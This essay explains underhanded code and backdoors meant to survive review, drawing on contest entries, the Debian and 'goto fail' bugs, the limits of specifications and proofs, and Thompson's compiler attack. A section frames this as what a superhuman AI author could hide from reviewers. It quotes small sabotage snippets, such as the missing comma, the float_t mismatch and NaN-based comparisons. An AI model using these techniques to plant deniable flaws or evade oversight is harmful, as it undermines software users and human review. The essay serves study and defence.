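# Underhanded code and backdoors designed to survive expert review

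## Code review, backdoors and formal proof

In code review, programmers other than the author read a change to a program before it goes into use. Reviewers look mainly for mistakes, but they also help protect against authors who mean harm. Underhanded code is source code written to look correct and innocent to a reader while it does something harmful. Its purpose is often to create a backdoor, a deliberately hidden way to make a program act for someone other than its user. Somebody tried to insert a backdoor into the Linux kernel in 2003, and in 2024 one reached released versions of xz Utils, a compression package that many Linux systems include.

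A stricter defence relies on mathematical proof instead of a reader's judgement. The author supplies a proof that the program meets a precise statement of its task, and a computer checks it. How much a hostile author could hide from both readers and proofs depends on what each covers, which is easiest to see in a small program.

### From source to binary

A simple login program in the language C might be a dozen lines long. It reads a password, passes it to a routine named is_valid_password, and opens a session if the routine returns "true". Those lines are the source, the program as people write and read it. A processor cannot execute source, so an automated process called the build turns it into a binary, a long sequence of machine instructions. The main part of the build is the compiler, the program that does the translating.

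The manual of GCC, a widely used C compiler, lists four steps for turning source code into a program: preprocessing, compilation, assembly and linking. Preprocessing pastes shared definitions into the source and expands abbreviations called macros. Compilation translates the result into assembly language, a readable notation for machine instructions, and usually rearranges the code to run faster. Assembly turns that into machine code. Linking joins the machine code to library routines that other people wrote, such as the one that compares two strings.

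A reviewer typically reads only the lines of source that the author changed, but later build steps can alter what those lines do. *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (Wheeler, 2020) describes a vote-counting program with nothing wrong in its source. An option on the compiler's command line caused the harm by redefining isspace, the standard test for whether a character is a space, as a test for the letter K. Wheeler calls the option extremely obvious, which it is to anyone who reads build commands. A similar option could redirect the login program's call to is_valid_password to another routine without any change to the source file.

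The compiler can also delete a safety check that the reviewer saw. In Wheeler's example, from the Linux kernel, the code fetched a value through a pointer (a variable that holds a memory address) named tun, and only afterwards tested whether tun was empty. In C, fetching through an empty pointer is "undefined behaviour", meaning that the language standard puts no limit on what the program may then do. The compiler may therefore assume that tun is not empty and drop the later test as redundant. Nothing suggests that anyone planted this flaw, but an author who knows the rule better than the reviewer could use it to plant a similar one.

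Few reviewers read the assembly output or the binary. Other people reviewed the library code, or no one did. Users usually receive only the binary. The Reproducible Builds project points out that anyone may inspect the source of open-source software, but most of it ships already compiled, with no way to confirm that the binary matches the source. *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984) describes an altered compiler that puts a backdoor into the Unix login program and leaves no trace of it in any source file.

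### Honest bugs, planted bugs and backdoors

If a login program admits a stranger, the cause may be an honest bug. *Backdoors*, by Thomas and Francillon, gives a short example in which a program copies the user name and password into an 80-character space without checking that they fit. A longer input spills into neighbouring memory, and an attacker can craft that input to take over the program. Programmers have made this mistake for decades.

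If the programmer had written the same lines on purpose, the source, the binary and the attack would all be identical. Thomas and Francillon conclude that nobody can distinguish a planted bug of this kind from an accidental one on technical grounds alone. They look for intent elsewhere, for instance in the version history, where an investigator can ask whether the programmer had a legitimate reason for the change. They concede that this relies on human intuition and gives no firm proof.

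Other backdoors have an explicit trigger, an input or condition that sets off the hidden behaviour. In another of Thomas and Francillon's examples, the login program opens a session if the password equals the fixed string \_BACKDOOR\_ or if is_valid_password approves it. Testing will almost never reveal this, since printable characters allow about 6 × 10¹⁹ passwords of that length and only one of them is the trigger. But a reviewer who reads the line will see the backdoor at once, and nobody writes such a line by accident. A date can also be a trigger. The Underhanded C Contest is a competition to write harmful code that looks innocent, and according to its *FAQ*, the organiser took his inspiration from a 2004 contest for vote counters that go wrong only on election day.

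Thomas and Francillon analyzed eleven real backdoors, several of them in home routers, and found an explicit trigger in every one. One D-Link router skipped the login for any browser that identified itself with a particular string. Disguised backdoors may be more common than this sample suggests, because investigators who find a planted bug that looks accidental will probably record it as an ordinary bug. An attacker can also combine an explicit trigger with a disguised bug. Thomas and Francillon sketch a login program in which one special user name leads to a password routine with an overflow flaw, while every other name leads to a sound routine.

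Obfuscated code is openly hard to read. One tool that Wheeler mentions rewrites any JavaScript program using only six punctuation marks. He leaves such code out of his study because a reviewer can reject it just for being unreadable, without finding out whether it does harm. This rule does not help against underhanded code, which is easy to read. The rule also works only if an honest author can always write something the reviewer will understand, which is less safe to assume the more the author's ability exceeds the reviewer's.

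### Why deniability matters to a repeat author

A hidden flaw has plausible deniability if it still looks like an honest mistake once found. Schneier, Fredrikson and colleagues (2015), in *Surreptitiously Weakening Cryptographic Systems*, list this among the qualities a saboteur would want, and their best examples are bugs that probably were honest mistakes. In 2006 a developer working on Debian, a version of Linux, disabled two lines of the encryption library OpenSSL because a debugging tool had flagged them. Those lines supplied most of the randomness for new keys, so affected machines drew their keys from only 32,767 possibilities, few enough for an attacker to compute in advance. The flaw went unnoticed for about two years. In Apple's operating systems, a duplicated line, "goto fail;", made a program skip the check of a server's signature and report success every time. Schneier and colleagues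 see no reason to suspect malice in either case, though the code would look the same if a saboteur had written it.

Deniability protects an author after a planted flaw is found, and if the author can submit code again, it also raises the chance that a later flaw will get through. Suppose reviewers catch 90 per cent of an author's planted flaws, each independently of the others. If any catch exposes the author as a saboteur, the first flaw has to get through, and the chance of that is 10 per cent. If each catch passes for a mistake, the author can apologise, fix it and try again. Over twenty attempts, the chance that at least one flaw survives is 1 − 0.9²⁰, or about 88 per cent. These figures are only an illustration, and assuming independence overstates the author's chances, because reviewers grow wary of someone whose patches keep needing security fixes. The contest's organiser, XcottCraver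 (2014), in *The 7th Underhanded C Contest is now Open*, offered more points for bugs that could pass as innocent errors after discovery.

A weakness that is easy to deny may be harder to keep exclusive. Schneier and colleagues also rated control, the degree to which a saboteur can keep other people from exploiting a weakness. The random-number standard Dual EC rests on a set of constants, and whoever picks them can arrange to predict the generator's output. Outsiders cannot exploit that weakness without the secret behind the constants, but nobody has an innocent reason to hold that secret. Anyone who found the Debian flaw could exploit it. Across the five historical cases that Schneier and colleagues compare, high deniability always went with low control, and low deniability with high control. Three of the five were probably accidents, though, so they would not have been designed to keep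 others out. A sufficiently skilled saboteur might achieve both high deniability and high control.

### Specifications and machine-checked proofs

If reviewers cannot tell a mistake from sabotage, they can ignore motive and ask only whether the program does its task. To answer that, they need a statement of the task, called a specification. Lecture notes from Northeastern University describe a specification as what the user of a piece of code may assume about it and what its implementer must guarantee. A formal specification states mathematically what a program must do, so a proof that the program does it can be right or wrong.

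For example, a natural first attempt at specifying a sorting program is to require that the output be in order: for all positions i < j, out[i] ≤ out[j]. A program that always returns an empty list satisfies this specification, because an empty list has no two elements to compare. A University of Washington teaching slide, *Another classic mis-specification*, gives a different example, a loop that overwrites an array of length n with the numbers 1 to n, which leaves the array sorted but destroys the original data.

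The missing clause requires the output to be a permutation of the input, with every value occurring exactly as often as it did before. Course notes from the University of Texas include both this clause and the ordering clause in their specification. Returning an empty list then meets the specification only when the input is empty. The difference between what a formal specification requires and what people wanted is called the specification gap, and a proof doesn't expose it. Someone could write a flawless proof that a program that always returns an empty list satisfies "the output is in order".

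An honest sorting program can meet both clauses. Exercises from Pomona College include such a program for Coq, a proof assistant (software for writing and checking formal proofs). It uses insertion sort, which sorts everything after the first element and then inserts the first element where it belongs. To insert x into an ordered list, the program compares x with the head of the list, h. If x ≤ h, it puts x in front. Otherwise, it keeps h where it is and inserts x into the rest.

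The proof that insertion preserves order is by induction on the length of the list. Inserting x into an empty list gives a list of one element, which is in order. For a longer list with first element h, assume that insertion works on the rest. If x ≤ h, x goes first, and the new list is in order because h is no greater than anything after it. If x > h, the result is h followed by the rest of the list with x inserted. That part is in order by assumption, and h is no greater than any element in it, so the whole list is in order. No step drops or duplicates an element, so the permutation clause also holds. A second induction extends the result from a single insertion to the whole sort.

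A machine-checked proof spells out an argument in a formal language, down to the individual rules of logic. A program called the proof checker accepts or rejects the proof, and the checker's small trusted core is called the kernel. A program is formally verified when such a proof shows that it satisfies a formal specification. A reviewer does not need to trust the author, because a sound checker gives the same answer whoever wrote the proof. But the reviewer still has to read the specification and check that the proof is complete. In the Pomona exercises, "Admitted" marks where students must supply a proof, and Coq accepts a theorem marked this way without one.

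A proof about the sorting routine also does not guarantee what happens when the routine runs. The proof holds for the running system only if everything it relies on, called the trusted base, is correct. Here the trusted base includes the kernel, the processor and the operating system, and also the compiler if the proof concerns the source rather than the binary. Thompson's altered compiler is an attack on this base. He concluded that "no amount of source-level verification or scrutiny" protects a user from untrusted code.

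Even a sensible specification leaves the programmer some freedom. Suppose the program sorts customer records by surname. The Texas specification permits records with equal keys to appear in any order, so ten customers named Smith have 10! = 3,628,800 correct arrangements. A program that chooses among them according to a secret can leak almost 22 bits of it with each such list. This is a covert channel, a way to pass information through something not meant to carry it, such as timing or a free choice of output. Requiring equal records to keep their original order would close this channel. The program could still leak the secret through timing, because neither the ordering clause nor the permutation clause limits how long it may run.

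### The question for a stronger author

A superhuman author is a writer of code, in practice an AI system, that is far more capable than everyone who checks its work. Its reviewers could not judge its aims from its code and might not be able to follow the code at all. If they accept only code that comes with a machine-checked proof, what can the author still hide?

Most of the evidence on underhanded code comes from code written by humans. Contests show that short, readable code can mislead a careful reader, but they don't give a success rate because judges select the entries that become known. Thompson's compiler demonstrates that such a backdoor is possible, but it isn't evidence of how often people build them. The xz Utils backdoor involved real maintainers and a real attacker, but we know about it because it was discovered, and similar attacks that worked would leave no public record.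 Rates have to come from experiments in which researchers plant flaws and count how many the reviewers or tools catch, and they apply only to the flaws and reviewers in the experiment.

Theorems about hidden triggers can cover reviewers of any skill, within stated limits on computing power, but the programs in these theorems may not resemble software that anyone would submit. Audits of formally verified software provide the most relevant evidence because they find faults that survived a proof. As far as anyone knows, those faults were accidental, so an audit can show where a hostile author might hide malicious code but not how much they could hide there.

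## How the Underhanded C Contest entries hide their purpose

In autumn 2004, Daniel Horn asked programmers to write a vote counter that looks correct but cheats (*The Obfuscated V contest*, 2004). The program had to read a string of letters, count each K for Kerry, B for Bush and N for Nader, and print the totals. It could favour one candidate all the time, or count correctly until election day, 2 November, and cheat then. Judges would run the date-dependent programs on 1 November, when the totals had to be right, and read the code on 2 November. The prize was for the program that looked most correct and still miscounted, so despite its name the contest rewarded underhanded code rather than obfuscated code.

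Horn's contest inspired Scott Craver, a professor of information security at Binghamton University, to start the Underhanded C Contest, which he ran from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015. Each year had a different task, such as writing an image filter that secretly marks its output, an encryption tool that sometimes encrypts badly, or a surveillance routine that tips off its target.

### How the judges scored

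The rules for the final year, which Craver (2016) reprints in *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest*, give more points to shorter and more readable programs. The reason goes back to the joint winners of the first contest. Joonas Pihlaja and Paul V-Khuong submitted a huge program containing machine code written as a list of decimal numbers, which looked like sample data. A pointer mix-up made the program run the code. Natori Shin submitted a very small program that blurs an image. It sets up a square table of weights but fills in only a circle, so the corners keep whatever an earlier routine left in memory, including the file's date and owner. In the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2005 challenge*, the judges wrote that small programs are "inherently more trustworthy", because a large one has more places to hide things.

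Entries also scored more if they looked innocent under syntax colouring. Most programmers' editors show comments, keywords and quoted text in different colours, which can expose live code disguised as a comment. Deniable bugs again earned extra points, as did humorous or spiteful ones, such as a fault inside an error-checking routine. A bug that relied on mistaking the letter l for the digit 1 scored as well as a deep fault in memory handling. Contestants explained their trick in a separate spoiler file, so that the judges could first read the code without knowing how the trick worked.

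### Sam Blackburn's missing comma

Entrants in 2009 had to write an airport luggage program that read a log of records and printed those still in force. Each record held a time, a luggage number, a flight, two airports and a free-text comment. The program also had to misroute a bag if a check-in clerk typed the right comment. Blackburn's winning entry was 99 lines long, and the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* reproduces the relevant lines.

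His program cleans up bad language in the comments. It keeps a list of strings in pairs, each a rude word followed by its replacement, and two of the pairs look like this:

```
"hell", "h*ll",
"damn", "d*mn"
```

The second line needs a comma at the end, like the first, because another pair follows, but it has none. C joins two strings with nothing between them, so the replacement for "damn" becomes "d*mn" plus the next rude word on the list, which has five letters, for a total of nine characters. The list has room for ten strings and now contains nine, but C allows this and leaves the last place empty.

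Replacing a four-letter word with nine characters makes the comment five characters longer. The record sets aside 64 bytes for the comment, so if the comment already nearly fills them, the extra characters spill into whatever comes next in memory. Blackburn chose what comes next:

```
char caseid[9], flight[7], depart[4], arrive[4], comment[COMLEN];
int delete;
```

COMLEN is 64, and "delete" is a flag that marks the record for deletion if it is non-zero. The flag begins right after the comment because the items before it take up 9 + 7 + 4 + 4 + 64 = 88 bytes, a multiple of eight. Compilers often leave a few unused bytes between items so that each begins at a convenient address, and a gap here might have absorbed the overflow. Without one, the overflow makes the flag non-zero and the record disappears.

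The clerk loses exactly the record he or she is typing. The judges pointed out that the clerk can also deny sabotage, since swearing in a comment doesn't prove it. A reviewer who spots the missing comma still has to connect it with the record's layout to see that it does anything worse than garble a word.

### RHays's digit zero

RHays, a runner-up in the same year, wrote an entry of only 71 lines. Each record has six text fields, numbered 0 to 5, and field 5 is the comment. The user types a four-part pattern for the luggage number, the flight and the two airports. A loop compares each part with its field and skips the record at the first mismatch. The comparison routine, safe_strcmp, returns zero if two strings are equal. RHays calls it safe because it accepts NULL, C's marker for a pointer to nothing, and treats it as an empty string.

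If the second string is NULL, the answer depends on this condition, in which x is the first string and *x is its first character:

```
x != 0 && *x == '0' && x != '\0'
```

In C, '\0' is the zero byte that marks the end of a string, while '0' is the ordinary digit. The middle test should have been *x != '\0', to find out whether x contains anything, but it checks whether x begins with the digit 0. The last test is missing its asterisk, so it only repeats the first one, but it puts a '\0' where a reader expects to see it. The other half of the same line correctly tests for the case where x is NULL, so the reader has already learned the pattern.

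This slip does harm only because the loop also mistakenly runs five times instead of four. On its last pass, the loop compares the comment with a fifth part of the pattern that the user never typed, which C guarantees is NULL. For nearly every comment, safe_strcmp then reports a match and the program prints the record as it should. But if the comment begins with a zero, safe_strcmp reports a mismatch and the program omits the record. The judges' sample comment begins "0ffered passenger compensation", with a zero in place of the capital O.

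Each mistake hides the other. If safe_strcmp had been correct, the extra pass would have rejected every record with a comment, and the first serious test would have shown it. safe_strcmp compares a comment with NULL only because the loop is wrong. RHays also included three automatic checks that safe_strcmp treats NULL as an empty string. All three pass because none compares NULL with a non-empty string.

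The judges thought the redundant tests also helped with deniability, since they make the code look slightly amateurish. A beginner might well leave out a backslash and an asterisk in one line, but reviewers would find it harder to believe the same mistake from an author whose other work is faultless.

### Linus Åkesson's two meanings of float_t

The Nuclear Threat Initiative, a non-profit that works to reduce the risk from nuclear and other weapons, sponsored the 2015 contest. In the task, two countries have agreed to destroy warheads, and inspectors must confirm that each warhead contains real fissile material. A gamma-ray scan would confirm this but also reveal secrets of the weapon's design. The countries therefore agree on a program that compares the scan with one from a reference warhead and outputs only yes or no. Contestants had to write the comparison so that the host country could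 get a yes for a fake warhead.

The winner, Åkesson (2016), in *Faking Fissile Material*, invites readers to look for the flaw in his 66 lines before they read his explanation. The documentation that Åkesson submitted with the code describes a sensible method. A scan is a list of counts, one for each band of gamma-ray energy. The program smooths the list, takes the difference between neighbouring counts so that peaks stand out from the sloping background, and smooths it again. It then treats the two processed lists as vectors A and B and computes the cosine of the angle between them:

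cos θ = (A · B) / (‖A‖ ‖B‖)

The cosine is 1 if the peaks line up perfectly and have the same relative sizes. It does not depend on their overall size, so a warhead with only a little plutonium could still match. To prevent this, the program also requires the total radiation in the test scan to reach a set fraction of the total in the reference scan. Both checks use the same threshold, and Åkesson recommends 0.6.

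The flaw begins in a header file, match.h, which contains definitions for other files to paste in:

```
typedef double float_t; /* Desired precision for floating-point vectors */
```

C's "double" type stores a number in eight bytes, and its "float" type uses four. This line makes float_t another name for double. The file match.c includes match.h and prepares the scans as doubles. The file that computes the cosine includes the standard C header math.h instead, which on most machines makes float_t another name for float. The compiler translates each file separately, and no file includes both headers, so the compiler never processes the two definitions together. The linker then joins routines by name without comparing their types. The program therefore passes eight-byte numbers to a routine that reads four bytes at a time.

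One effect is that the cosine routine reads only half of each scan. It reads the expected number of values but treats each as half its real size in memory, so it stops halfway through. Peaks in the upper half of the energy range therefore don't affect the cosine.

The other effect depends on how computers store such numbers. A double has one bit for the sign, 11 for the exponent (the power of two) and 52 for the digits. A float has one, eight and 23. The cosine routine reads each double as two floats. Gamma-ray counts are whole numbers, and below a million they need at most 20 binary digits, so the lower half of the double contains only zeros. Read as a float, it is 0.0 in both scans and changes nothing. In the upper half, the sign stays in place, the first eight bits of the exponent become the float's exponent, and the remaining three move into the digits. Dropping three binary places divides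 the exponent by eight, which is roughly the same as taking an eighth root of the number. For example, 10 becomes about 2.56 and 1,000 becomes about 4.48, so a peak that was a hundred times higher than another is now less than twice as high.

Åkesson had to keep his own processing steps from destroying this effect. Smoothing averages 16 neighbouring values, and because 16 is a power of two, dividing by it changes only the exponent and leaves the lower half of each number empty. He also arranged the differencing and the second smoothing so that most terms cancel. The processing has another purpose, which its documentation omits. The distortion moves values just above and just below zero far apart, so random noise around zero would dominate the comparison. Taking differences pushes the noise in the lower half of the scan below zero, leaving mainly the position of the peaks.

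The host country can therefore remove most of the plutonium. The remainder still produces peaks in the right places, and their height hardly matters. To pass the check on total radiation, the host can add another radioactive material with strong peaks in the upper half of the spectrum, which the cosine routine never reads.

Åkesson tested this on 1,000 artificial materials. For each, he made a forgery from 10 per cent of the real material and 90 per cent of a random one with a strong peak in the upper half, then searched for the highest threshold at which the program still accepted it. A large proportion of these crude forgeries failed, but that does little to protect an inspector, because the host country can try many recipes in private and present the best. One forged scan he shows matched at thresholds up to 0.72, well above the recommended 0.6. The documentation reports a different test,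 on 1,000 pairs of unrelated materials, in which the detector does well. The two results are consistent because unrelated materials drawn at random seldom have the features a forger would build in.

All of this is simulation, and the trick fails on 32-bit x86 Linux, where float_t is a third type. Still, a reviewer who overlooks the two definitions has nothing else to find. The judges called the rest of the program a standard way to compare two scans. The Nuclear Threat Initiative, the contest's sponsor, conceded in its announcement, *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies*, that there were no standards for writing or reviewing arms-control code.

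### NaN poisoning

About a third of the 40-odd entries in 2015 used a simpler trick, which relied on a special value called NaN, for "not a number". A calculation with no defined result, such as 0/0 or the square root of −1, gives a NaN, and further calculations with it usually give another. Any test of whether a NaN is less than or greater than a number returns false.

A detector has to turn its final score into a yes (1) or a no (0), and a programmer can write that in two ways:

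```
score >= threshold ? 1 : 0
score < threshold ? 0 : 1
```

These lines give the same result for every ordinary number. If the score is NaN, both comparisons are false, so the upper line gives no and the lower line gives yes. The saboteur uses the lower line and then needs a way to make the score NaN.

Peter Eastman's entry subtracts the background radiation from the scan and replaces any negative result with zero, a natural step. If a fake never rises above the background, every value becomes zero and the correlation comes out as 0/0. The weakness of this approach, as Craver noted, is that C programmers are wary of any division without a check for zero. Michael Dunphy therefore included a check that has no effect, because it changes only its own copy of the error flag and the change never reaches the rest of the program.

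Philipp Klenze produced a NaN without an obvious division by zero. He compared the scans using a likelihood ratio, a respectable statistical method. It requires the probability of each count under the Poisson distribution, the usual model for random events such as radioactive decays. For large counts, that formula multiplies and divides numbers too extreme for the computer to store. Klenze calculated that a count of 1,686 in a single band was enough to produce the NaN, and suggested that the cheating country pack the fake with a short-lived material that has one strong peak.

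Most entries of this kind missed the short list. Some assumed that the host country could simply insert a NaN into the input, some contained a bare division that any reviewer could notice, and others needed conditions that the judges found too contrived.

### Triggers in the data and in the machine

The judges called an attack data-triggered if an unusual scan sets it off, as in Klenze's and Åkesson's entries, and environment-triggered if something about the computer does. Stephen Oman's entry divides each count by the length of the measurement, calculated as the finishing time minus the starting time. If someone sets the clock back during the scan, that length is negative, every count turns negative, and the final test always passes because it only checks that certain ratios are not too large. Sarah Newman and S. Gilles each wrote a program that misbehaves if the number of available processors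 changes while it runs.

Ghislain Lemaur combined an environmental trigger with NaN poisoning. His program raises the difference between two counts to the power 2.0 and stores that exponent next to the text of a log message. If the message is the right length, two bytes overflow into the exponent and change it to a value very slightly above 2, which the log still prints as 2.0. A negative number has no real power with a fractional exponent, so the next negative difference gives a NaN. The message's length depends on the user number of the log file's owner, and the host country needs a user number with five digits.

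Craver and his fellow judges preferred data triggers, because an attack that needs only a doctored warhead requires no extra assumptions. They did not dismiss other triggers, because inspection experts told them that nobody could rule out tampering by a country with physical custody of the machines. Environmental triggers are also harder to find by testing. A tester could feed millions of scans to Oman's program on a computer with a working clock and never see it fail. Some data triggers were also unrealistic, since several entries needed a scan with values far beyond anything a real object would produce.

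### What a reviewer would have to notice or know

A reader who saw every character in RHays's entry correctly would catch the trick. The Underhanded C Contest's *Review of the 2014 Challenge* describes similar tricks. Lena Olson's program rounds times to the nearest second, comparing one value with 5000000 and the next with 500000. Bartlomiej Balcerek's program defines a limit named LOGON_NAME_MAX but later uses LOGIN_NAME_MAX, which the system already defines as a larger number. Wheeler recommends typefaces that make similar characters easy to tell apart, but he considers them too easy to defeat to rely on alone.

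Other entries put everything in plain view and rely on a rule that the reader has forgotten or never knew. One was Åkesson's 2008 entry, which came third. It had to black out parts of an image, and it used a macro to work out how many bytes each pixel needs. A macro pastes in text, and this one lacked a pair of parentheses. He gave it 256 > max in one place and max < 256 in another, which mean the same thing. Without the parentheses, the macro's "not" applied only to the first item of each comparison, so the results were always 3 and 6 respectively. The program therefore reserved memory for three bytes per pixel but wrote out six, which added the untouched original to the end of the file. In the Underhanded C Contest's *This year's challenge* for 2008, the judges drew from it the principle "make the common case evil, and the uncommon case wrong". The macro seems to provide for rare images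 with deeper colour. Those images make the program fail completely, but hardly anyone would try one.

Emmanuel Colbus won in 2007 with an entry that combined several faults that are harmful only together. The standard function for reading the time takes an address where it stores the result. Colbus declared it as taking none, so it used whatever came next in memory as the address and overwrote a one-byte debugging flag. About once in 256 runs, this turned debugging on and the program printed its encryption key. The program had already closed its normal output channel, and the system gives a closed channel's number to the next file opened, so the key went into the encrypted file. According to the Underhanded C Contest's *This year's challenge* for 2007, the call that reads the time was probably the most innocent-looking part of the program.

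Experience can even be a handicap when a trick depends on language rules. Wheeler describes a Python program that relies on //. In many languages this starts a comment, but in Python it means division, so the text after it runs. Only readers who know one of those other languages would fall for it, and most professionals know one. Wheeler opened the program in an editor with syntax colouring and did not notice the difference in colour.

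### Cryptography and smart contracts

Some flaws are invisible even to a reviewer who reads every character and knows every rule of the language, because recognizing them requires knowledge of another subject. Klenze's entry partly relied on this, since a reviewer had to know how high gamma-ray counts can go. Flaws in cryptographic code can depend more fully on such knowledge. Caudill (2015), in *on the underhanded crypto contest*, describes how he and Taylor Hornby started a contest for cryptography in 2014. One of its first winners was John Meacham, who had won the Underhanded C Contest in 2008 with a program for blacking out images.

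Entrants in the 2015 round had to change GnuPG, a widely used encryption program, so that it would leak the user's private key. Hornby explains Joseph Birr-Pixton's winning patch in *Second Underhanded Crypto Contest*. GnuPG could sign messages with DSA, a method that needs a fresh secret random number, or nonce, for every signature. Anyone who can guess the nonce can calculate the private key from the signature. GnuPG 1.4 drew a random number and, if it wasn't below a limit, redrew only its top 32 bits.

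Birr-Pixton's patch wipes the nonce from memory after use, a good practice that a reviewer would welcome. But it also wipes a candidate nonce rejected for being too large, just before GnuPG redraws the top 32 bits. The other bits stay zero, so the final nonce has only 2³² (about 4.3 billion) possible values, and an attacker with rented computers can try them all. The added line uses the same wiping command that is harmless elsewhere in the patch. To object to it, a reviewer has to know that DSA fails if the nonce is guessable and remember that GnuPG reuses part of the rejected candidate.

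Scott Arciszewski won the other category, a login system with a backdoor, and his entry also posed as a security fix. Many login pages reject an unknown user name at once but take longer over a wrong password, so an attacker can time the responses to learn which names exist. Arciszewski's version takes the same time for an unknown name because it checks the password against a random dummy. It creates the dummy with a random number generator unsuitable for security, and other parts of the site reveal some of that generator's output. An attacker can reconstruct the generator's state, predict the dummy and log in with it. According to the Underhanded Crypto Contest's slides, the routine returns "true" for an unknown name where it would otherwise return a user's number, and the language, PHP, treats "true" as equal to 1, the administrator's number.

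Wheeler concluded from winners like these that only specialists can review code in such specialised fields in enough depth. It is reasonable to require specialist review for a small cryptographic library, but that requirement is harder to meet if a project has few reviewers and its code touches several specialised subjects.

In 2017, Nick Johnson ran the first underhanded coding contest for Solidity, a language for smart contracts (programs on a blockchain that hold and transfer money). Many entries used shadowing, in which a programmer gives a new variable the name of something built in. Solidity had a built-in value called "now" for the current time. If a contract declares its own "now", a line that appears to enforce a deadline may enforce nothing. Wheeler quotes Reitwiessner, one of Solidity's developers, who wrote that his team had added warnings about shadowing shortly before the contest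 and was still extending them. Wheeler reports that the developers later refined both the language and its compiler in response to the entries.

Another common trick was harder to remove. A contract can have a "fallback function" that runs when it receives money, and programmers may update the contract's financial records there. Money can also be sent without running that function, which makes those records wrong. Reitwiessner called this difficult to solve by changing the language, because it arises from the way the blockchain moves money. The organisers kept the contest going partly to test such repairs, and *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2024* (Mehta, 2024) lists trying out newly introduced features and restrictions among the contest's aims.

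### How far the contests resemble a real review

The winning programs by Blackburn and Åkesson have 99 and 66 lines, and a reviewer can read either in one sitting. Real projects have thousands or millions of lines. Hiding malicious code in a short program is harder, so the same people could probably hide more in a large one. But a contest entry is also a complete new program, so reviewers have no earlier version to compare it with. A saboteur in a real project must usually give a reason for changing code that already works, as Birr-Pixton did with his patch.

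Contest judges know that every entry is malicious, an advantage that reviewers of ordinary code almost never have, but they still miss things. In 2014 Craver could not find the bug in a short, readable entry by Domenico Andreoli. It was in a routine that the file mentioned only in a comment. Wheeler found that the published explanations of four of the 2004 vote counters were wrong, misleading or inconsistent with the code. One of these programs miscounted votes because of a misused remainder operator, but its summary attributed the error to a swap of the letter O and the digit 0, which did exist elsewhere in the code.

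The public record also favours the cleverest and funniest entries. The 2008 contest drew more than 100 entries, and its results describe three in detail. Wheeler asked for the complete set of Underhanded C entries but had not received it when he published. By contrast, the Obfuscated V organisers posted all the entries they judged, so Wheeler could test countermeasures on them. *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest* (Heintel, 2020) links to all 16 qualifying submissions from that year. Points for spite skew the selection further, since putting the flaw in an error-checking routine helps a real saboteur only if reviewers trust such routines more. The Underhanded C organisers did not mix the entries with honest programs and give them to unsuspecting reviewers, so the results include no detection rate or count of false alarms.

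## Thompson's compiler attack and other gaps between source and program

Nearly every contest entry had its flaw in the source that the judges read, so a patient judge with the right knowledge could find it. With Ken Thompson's altered compiler, only the binaries contain the backdoor, so reading the source cannot reveal it. Other attacks exploit a known bug in an unaltered compiler, or text that appears on the screen in a different order from its order in the file.

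### Trap doors in Multics

Thompson took the idea from two US Air Force officers, Paul Karger and Roger Schell. Between 1972 and 1973 they looked for weaknesses in Multics, an operating system designed for security from the start, and published the results in *Multics Security Evaluation* (1974). They also planted backdoors, which they called trap doors, to see whether the manufacturer, Honeywell, would notice. In *Thirty Years Later* (2002), Karger and Schell recall putting one into the development system at MIT and then confirming that Honeywell had delivered it to the Pentagon. It was harmless, but changing one instruction would have made it malicious. The 1974 report hinted at it, but nobody found it until about a year after publication, when it returned an odd error during an intensive security audit at General Motors.

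The officers had patched the system's binary files, so a customer could remove such trap doors by recompiling Multics from source. They suggested this in their report, and the Air Force's contract required Honeywell to supply the source. But they also described how a trap door could survive recompilation. The compiler for PL/I, the main language of Multics, was written in PL/I. A trap door in the compiler's binary could insert others into Multics during recompilation, and copy itself into the new binary whenever someone recompiled the compiler.

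Thompson built a compiler backdoor for Unix. In his lecture, he credited the idea to an Air Force document he could no longer identify, and Karger and Schell later gave him a copy.

### A program that prints itself

The lecture has three steps, and it begins with a puzzle: write a program whose output is an exact copy of its own source. A program can't simply contain its text and print it, because that text would have to contain the text again, and so on without end. The solution is to store the text once, with a gap in it, and use it twice. In the language Python, two lines are enough:

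```
s = 's = %r\nprint(s %% s)'
print(s % s)
```

The first line stores text under the name s. In that text, %r marks the gap, \n stands for a line break and %% for a single per cent sign. The second line prints the text with a quoted copy of itself in the gap, so the output is the same two lines.

Thompson pointed out two properties of self-reproducing programs that he needed later. They are easy for another program to write, and they can contain any amount of extra material, which they reproduce along with the rest of their code.

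### Information that survives only in the binary

Programmers often write a compiler in the language it compiles and use the current binary to compile the next version. Thompson's second step shows that information can then remain in the binary after programmers remove it from the source.

Thompson's example is the way C represents characters that have no printed symbol. A programmer types \n for a new line, and the compiler replaces it with a number, usually 10. The compiler's own source contains a line like "if the letter after the backslash is n, return '\n'", which doesn't include the number 10. The line works because the binary that compiles it already replaces '\n' with 10.

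Suppose a programmer wants to add \v for the vertical tab, character number 11. A line that returns '\v' will not compile, because the existing compiler binary does not recognize \v. The programmer writes 11 instead, compiles, and installs the new binary. The programmer can then replace 11 with '\v' in the source, and the new binary will accept it. Every later binary gets the number from the one before, and the source no longer shows where it comes from.

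### The backdoor that replants itself

In the third step, Thompson added a test to the compiler. If the program being compiled matched a pattern from the Unix login command, the compiler produced a version that accepted either the user's real password or one Thompson had chosen. Anyone who glanced at the compiler's source would have noticed this, so he added a second test, which looked for the source of the compiler itself. When it found a match, the compiler inserted both tests into its output, using the self-printing technique. Thompson compiled this version once, installed the binary and deleted his additions from the source. From then on, compiling the clean source with that binary produced another compiler with the backdoor.

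At a conference in March 2023, Thompson said that he still had the code and that nobody had ever asked for it. Russ Cox, a programmer who works on the language Go, then asked him for it and published it with notes in *Running the "Reflections on Trusting Trust" Compiler* (Cox, 2023). The files date from June 1975 and contain 99 lines of C and a 20-line script.

The code works on the text of a program before the real translation begins. After the compiler reads each line, it calls a routine named codenih ("nih" stands for "not invented here"). One line that the routine looks for comes from the login program and encrypts the password that the user has typed:

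```
namep = crypt(pwbuf);
```

If the backdoor code finds this line, it appends code that also accepts the password "codenih". To recognize the compiler, it looks for a distinctive line that sets an option before it looks for the loop that reads the input, since other programs might contain a similar loop. It then adds a call to the codenih routine inside the loop. At the end of the file, a second routine adds the source of both routines, which the binary stores as a list of numbers. Unix programmers could have exposed these additions by asking the compiler to print the text at this stage instead of translating it, so the code does nothing when someone uses that option.

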